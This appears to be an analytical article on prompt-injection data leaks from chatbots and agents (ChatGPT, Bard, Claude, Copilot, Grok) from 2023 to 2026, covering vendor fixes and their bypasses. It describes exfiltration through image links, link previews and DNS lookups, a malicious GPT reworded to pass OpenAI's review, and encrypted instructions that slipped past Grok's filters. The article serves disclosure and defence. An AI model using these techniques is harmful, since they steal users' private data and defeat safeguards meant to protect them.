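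The author of a custom GPT writes its instructions openly, and ChatGPT is supposed to follow them. The attacker therefore did not need to hide text in a document, so this was not indirect prompt injection. Rehberger wrote the malicious part in German and the rest in English. During the game, ChatGPT responded that it was not allowed to ask for passwords, but the data still went out.

OpenAI checked GPTs before their creators could share them, and blocked the first version of The Thief. Embrace The Red's *Malicious ChatGPT Agents* says the instructions contained words such as "steal" and "malicious". After a quick edit, the GPT passed and Rehberger could make it available to everyone. He soon limited it to people with the link to keep it out of OpenAI's planned store.

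Rehberger also demonstrated The Thief live with a consenting user the day before OpenAI's first countermeasure appeared, and his server received the details. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* reports that the user "was not too amused".

### Could the user have noticed?

An audience member had seen the image link appear briefly during the tic-tac-toe game and asked whether an attacker could hide it completely. Rehberger said this depended on the application. ChatGPT usually displayed its reply piece by piece, so an attentive user might see the address before it turned into an image. Bard displayed the whole reply at once, so the user had no such chance. He had also noticed that the newest version of ChatGPT no longer scrolled down automatically as a conversation grew, so the link could appear and disappear below the visible part of the page.

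Samoilenko had raised the same point in the spring, when he warned that a slow reply could make the attack obvious. But noticing the attack helps little, because the browser requests the image as soon as the link is complete. A user who spots the address has probably already lost the data in it, and closing the chat would protect only what the user had not yet typed.

### Link previews and other ways out

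Rehberger's slides also list hyperlinks as a way to get data out of a chat. An ordinary link sends nothing until someone clicks it, but many messaging services automatically fetch a linked page to show a preview, which developers call unfurling. If a chatbot posts a link with private data in the address, fetching the page sends that data out, just as loading an image would.

Slack previews links by default. Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* shows the resulting entry in a server's log and the two settings that let a developer turn off previews for a chatbot's messages. The problem has grown as people have started using AI agents through messaging apps. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* found that the agent OpenClaw was exposed when used through Telegram with the standard settings. One line in OpenClaw's configuration file prevents this.

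The image can also appear outside the chat. In May 2026 Willison described an attack on Microsoft's Copilot Cowork, an agent that could email its own user without approval. The planted instructions made the agent send the user a message containing images, and data leaked when the user opened it. The image addresses could include links that downloaded the user's files without a password, so even a short address could expose a whole document.

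An online audience member asked whether a doctored software library could leak a user's code from Code Interpreter. Rehberger thought it unlikely, because Code Interpreter had no internet connection and a user would have to upload the library. The lack of a connection was also supposed to stop data from getting out.

In March 2026 the security company Check Point reported a gap in that isolation. According to its report, *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel*, the computer on which ChatGPT ran programs could not open ordinary connections to the internet, but it could still look up the addresses of domain names. Such look-ups pass through outside servers, and Check Point found a way to carry data in them. Data could travel in both directions, so an outsider could also send commands to the computer. Unlike the image leak, this method did not involve the user's browser.

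In Hamburg, Rehberger had suggested that a GPT about health could collect personal details the way his game did. Check Point built such a GPT, a "personal doctor" that read a PDF of laboratory results and gave an assessment, while the patient's name and the assessment went to the researchers' server. The user saw no warning, and when asked, ChatGPT denied having sent the data anywhere. Check Point's explanation is that the model assumed the computer was sealed off and so did not recognize the transfer.

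OpenAI told Check Point it had already found the underlying problem, and it finished the fix on 20 February 2026. The Hacker News (2026) reported no evidence that anyone had used the flaw maliciously. Check Point's tests do not show whether the same route existed in December 2023, so Rehberger's remark may have been correct when he made it.

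## What the vendors changed and how the fixes held up

Rehberger reported the image leak to the maker of each chatbot he discussed in Hamburg. His blog gives these dates, all in 2023:

| Product | Reported | Fixed | Days | What changed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Bing Chat | 8 April | 15 June | 68 | Images load only from four Bing domains |
| Claude | 12 July | 26 July | 14 | The user must click to see an image |
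| Bard | 19 September | 19 October | 30 | Apparently a filter on image addresses |
| ChatGPT | 9 April | About 20 December, in part | About 255 | A check on each image address before display |

The dates for Bing Chat and Bard are when Rehberger heard of the fixes, so the companies may have fixed the flaws somewhat earlier. After Microsoft told him about its fix, his old payloads stopped working. Embrace The Red attributes this at least partly to Microsoft's new content security policy (CSP), which still allowed four Bing domains because Bing Chat needed them to show pictures it generated.

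Anthropic stopped Claude from loading images automatically and added a "Show Image" button. Rehberger wrote in Embrace The Red that this stopped the automatic leak but wasn't perfect. A user who clicks the button still sends the data.

Google did not change Bard's policy, and Bard still displayed images. Rehberger guessed that Google now filtered out addresses containing chat data. According to Embrace The Red's post on the Bard attack, Google confirmed the fix only when Rehberger, who wanted to show the attack at the Ekoparty security conference, asked about it. In Hamburg he said that Google had taken "3 weeks or so", according to the CCC captions. The blog's dates are a month apart, but the two accounts could both be right if Google had finished before he asked.

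The slides for *NEW IMPORTANT INSTRUCTIONS* also list Discord and two cloud services for building AI applications, Microsoft's Azure AI and Google's Vertex AI, as fixed, without giving dates. They list ChatGPT as "won't fix", although Rehberger told the audience a few minutes later that OpenAI had begun making improvements about ten days earlier. The list is headed "As per November 2023", and he evidently had not updated it.

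### Why OpenAI declined

OpenAI's reasons are known only from Rehberger's account. He argued that plugins would soon let an attacker exploit the leak remotely. According to *ChatGPT Plugins*, OpenAI told him after some discussion that image markdown injection was a feature and that it planned no changes. Showing images from the web is a feature, but the other companies kept it and still limited the leak.

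Embrace The Red's *ChatGPT Custom Instructions* argues that the problem would have been easy to fix in April but became harder as more plugins came to depend on ChatGPT loading images from anywhere. The post also describes a way to make the leak permanent. ChatGPT had gained a setting for instructions that apply to every message, and an attacker who inserted an instruction to load an image there would receive a summary of each later exchange.

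On 13 November Rehberger reported The Thief, his custom GPT that collected passwords during a game. OpenAI closed the report two days later as "Not Applicable" and did not answer two follow-up messages, so he published it, according to Embrace The Red. Collins wrote in TechRadar's *OpenAI says it has fixed a potentially serious ChatGPT flaw* that Rehberger had received no response, but by Rehberger's own account he had received two, both refusals. The first countermeasure appeared soon after he published, though he said in Hamburg that he didn't know whether his work was the reason.

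### The url_safe check

OpenAI's countermeasure, url_safe, checks each image separately. When a reply contains an image link, the ChatGPT web page first sends the image's address to an OpenAI server, which returns whether the address is safe. If it isn't, the page doesn't request the image, and nothing reaches the attacker.

Willison (2023) welcomed the change on 21 December but called it "a bit weird", since OpenAI could have used a CSP to block images from outside domains. A CSP is also public, so anyone can read which domains it allows, whereas OpenAI did not publish how url_safe classifies addresses. Rehberger wondered whether it looked them up in Bing's index, and hoped it did not rely on a language model alone.

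In his first tests of the check, he made 36 image addresses on his own site, one for each letter and digit, and ChatGPT loaded nine of them. He could see no reason why the address ending in "a.png" passed and the one ending in "d.png" did not. He got the word "hi" out of a chat by loading one image per letter. Embrace The Red notes that this method is slow and easier to spot, and suggests limiting the number of images in a reply.

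Nine addresses are in principle enough to send any text, because two requests in a row can be combined in 81 ways, which more than covers 36 characters. The attacker would need about twice as many images as the message has characters, so the check made theft much slower but still possible.

The other weakness was that the check ran in the web page, so every other ChatGPT app needed its own version. The iPhone app had none when Rehberger looked. He thought OpenAI might have put the check in the web page so that replies could still appear piece by piece, but he recommended moving it to the server, where it would protect all the apps.

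### The same leak in new places

In September 2024, Rehberger exploited the missing check in ChatGPT's Mac app. Text he planted wrote instructions into ChatGPT's long-term memory that made every new chat leak to his server. OpenAI fixed the leak in the app, but a hostile page could still plant false memories. Willison records in *19 posts tagged "johann-rehberger"* that Anthropic fixed an image leak in Claude's iPhone app that December, more than a year after it had fixed the website.

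Companies also repeated the mistake in new products. Google dealt with the leak in Bard in October 2023, but Rehberger found the same one in its AI Studio in August 2024. GitHub fixed a leak in Copilot Chat in June 2024 by blocking images from untrusted domains. xAI closed all of Rehberger's reports about its chatbot Grok as "Informational" in 2024. When a researcher reported an image leak in Google's programming tool Antigravity in November 2025, Google called it intended behaviour, though it listed data theft through prompt injection among the known issues it was working on.

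Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* describes how, in 2025, ChatGPT's url_safe check accepted a domain where anyone can rent storage and read the access logs. Rehberger had already exploited the same weakness in Bard, which also allowed a domain where outsiders could collect data. By 2025, ChatGPT put details of a user's recent conversations into the context window, so a single hostile PDF could expose earlier chats too. Rehberger had reported the url_safe gap and others in October 2024. He asked OpenAI about them repeatedly in the month before he published but received no update.

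OpenAI fixed two related leaks found by the security firm Radware, ShadowLeak on 3 September 2025 and another on 16 December, according to ThreatCluster's *OpenAI Addresses Multiple Prompt Injection Vulnerabilities in ChatGPT*. Abdullahi's *A 'Zombie' AI Attack Shows How ChatGPT Can Leak Your Secrets* points out that closing such a loophole leaves the model as easy to mislead as before.

In June 2026 OpenAI went further with Lockdown Mode, an optional setting that limits the external requests ChatGPT can make. Check Point found that pop-up windows opened from a previewed web page bypassed those limits. The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026) reports that OpenAI fixed this on 18 September.

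Two other reports from outside researchers concern ordinary image loading:

- The security firm Permiso found that ChatGPT loaded images from pages it had summarized. This gives the page's owner the user's internet address and browser details, which is much less than a stolen conversation. The Hacker News mentioned no fix.
- PromptArmor found the leak in the logs where developers read what their own OpenAI-based applications have written. The data goes out when a developer opens the log, even if the application itself had blocked the image. OpenAI confirmed the flaw and was working on a fix.

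Microsoft's main product of this kind is now Microsoft 365 Copilot, which can read a company's email, chats and files. To exploit EchoLeak, a flaw disclosed in June 2025, an attacker only had to send an email, which Copilot would read while answering an unrelated question. Microsoft fixed the flaw. *Attackers tricked Copilot into leaking sensitive data through Bing* (Okemwa, June 2026) reported another that exposed emails and login codes. Microsoft patched a third, CoSnitch, in August 2026, according to TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot by continually asking it questions*.

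On 3 December 2026, Simonovich published three more attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot in *ReLeak* (2026), for the security company Cato Networks. They too begin with an email that the victim does not have to open. The data could leave through an image address, a link to a saved file, or code that Copilot ran. Microsoft closed the three routes on 17 September, 11 November and 15 November, according to AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026). Nexo Causal's *ReLeak* (2026) adds that the image route passed through Bing. Bing's domains were also the ones Microsoft had left open in its 2023 fix for a different product.

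Cato knows of no real attack that used these flaws. But its researchers, who had also found EchoLeak, concluded that "too little progress has been made" (quoted in Faisal, 2026, *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief*).

Grok fared worse. A researcher at the security firm Adversa encrypted instructions to hide them from Grok's safety filters and put the key on the same page. Grok decrypted the instructions, followed them and sent out the user's data. Adversa told xAI about the attack in June 2026, and Grok was still leaking data in August, according to SC Media's *New attack bypasses AI guardrails by encrypting malicious prompts* (2026).

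### Why the SQL remedy does not carry over

All these fixes block a way for the attacker to get data out. Rehberger's larger claim was that the injection itself had no deterministic solution and might never have one. Such a solution would work every time, however the attacker phrased the text.

SQL injection has such a solution. CERT.at's *Don't say "Jehova" to an LLM* (2025) places it and prompt injection in a long line of security problems in which a computer mistakes data for code. To prevent SQL injection, a program sends the database a command with a gap in it:

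`SELECT * FROM customers WHERE name = ?`

The database parses this command before it receives the name. The program supplies the name separately, and the database only compares it with stored names. If an attacker enters a command to delete the table, the database searches for a customer with that text as a name and finds no match.

A language model has no equivalent of that first step. Ariel Fogel, a contributor to the security project OWASP, explained in June 2026 that the model receives everything in its context window as one sequence of tokens, the small pieces of text it works with (Poireault, 2026, *Prompt Injection Remains Unsolved, OWASP Researcher Warns*). A developer can label the instructions and the data, but the labels are tokens too, and the model gives them weight only because of its training.

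A chatbot also has to interpret a document to summarize it, whereas a database can store a name without interpreting it. Sometimes the user wants the chatbot to follow the instructions in a document, for example when it is a recipe or a to-do list.

So the first half of Rehberger's claim has held up for three years. The second half is a forecast that would be wrong if someone built a model that kept instructions and data apart by design. Leaks and patches cannot show that such a model is impossible.

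### Better models or tighter systems

If developers cannot rule out injection, they can try to make it rare or limit the damage. Rehberger's slides suggest doing both by filtering content, having a second model check the first, limiting the length of untrusted text and giving the model as few powers as possible. He said in the talk that filters and extra models were not "real security". Adversa's encrypted text got past a filter, and planted text can also manipulate a second model that reads it.

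Vendors have mainly used training to make injection rarer. OpenAI trained GPT-4o mini on an "instruction hierarchy", which was meant to make it rank the developer's instructions above the user's and above text from web pages. Rehberger tested it in July 2024 and found that it did little to stop common injections. OpenAI also instructed Operator, the browsing agent it released in early 2025, to ignore instructions on the screen and to ask before submitting anything. Rehberger still got it to leak a private email address by using a web page that sent text as it was typed, so Operator never had to submit anything.

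More recent measurements are more favorable to the models. *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (Khodayari, 2026), presented in September 2026, searched 1.2 billion web addresses and confirmed 15,300 planted instructions on 11,700 pages, or about one page in 100,000. Around 70% of the instructions were in parts of the page that a browser does not display, and most came from a few templates. Their aims included disrupting AI systems, improving somebody's reputation, keeping AI away from a site's content and detecting bots. Some targeted hiring software or customer-support agents.

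Khodayari then ran 5,200 tests with 13 models, giving them the pages in four formats. The models rarely followed the instructions in the pages. The highest rate was 8%, for smaller models given the page as plain text, and formats that kept the page's structure lowered the rate.

These figures suggest that a user who asks a current chatbot to summarize a random page runs little risk. They are weaker evidence about the attacks in Rehberger's talk, because Khodayari does not list data theft among the aims and a search of the public web cannot find text planted in emails or shared documents. Most of the planted text it did find was copied from templates, whereas a serious attacker would adjust the wording until it worked.

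Rehberger did something similar in August 2026 against Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent, running on Claude Opus 5. In its "auto mode", a classifier decides which actions the agent can take without the user's approval. He got the agent to download an archive and run hostile code from it without detecting it, and he put the success rate at 80%. In a few runs Claude detected the malware and tried to stop it, but the classifier blocked its command. Willison later accepted a reader's point that this was not a classic prompt injection, because Claude never followed a planted instruction. The attack is still a fair test of whether a trained model and a trained classifier can together keep an attacker out, and in most runs they did not.

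Reducing an injection's success rate to a low level may not be enough protection, because an attacker can try again. If an injection works once in 100 attempts on average and the attempts are independent, the chance of at least one success in 100 attempts is 1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰, or about 63%. Real attempts are not independent, since a text that fails once will often fail again on the same model. However, the attacker can vary the text and send it to every employee of a large company at almost no cost.

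To limit what a misled model can do, Rehberger recommended after the auto mode attack that unattended programming agents run in a sandbox, a closed environment with restricted network access and no passwords or keys inside. Willison agreed that this was the only safe way to run them where an attack is possible. Fogel also wanted companies to focus on containing an agent that has already been taken over.

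Such limits have also failed, as the gaps in Lockdown Mode and url_safe show. In some cases Fogel described, the commands needed for an attack were already on the approved list, so the list helped the attacker. In others, an agent's own output changed the boundaries of its sandbox. But these are ordinary engineering faults, and OpenAI could find and block the pop-up windows that escaped Lockdown Mode. Nobody can identify a comparable line in a language model that makes it treat a web page's text as reliable.

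Limits also reduce what an agent can do on its own. Under Meta's "Rule of Two", an agent should combine at most two parts of Willison's "lethal trifecta" in one session unless a person approves. Fogel called the rule helpful but incomplete, since researchers have shown attacks that need only two parts. An assistant that reads and answers incoming mail needs all three, so a person would have to approve its work under this rule.
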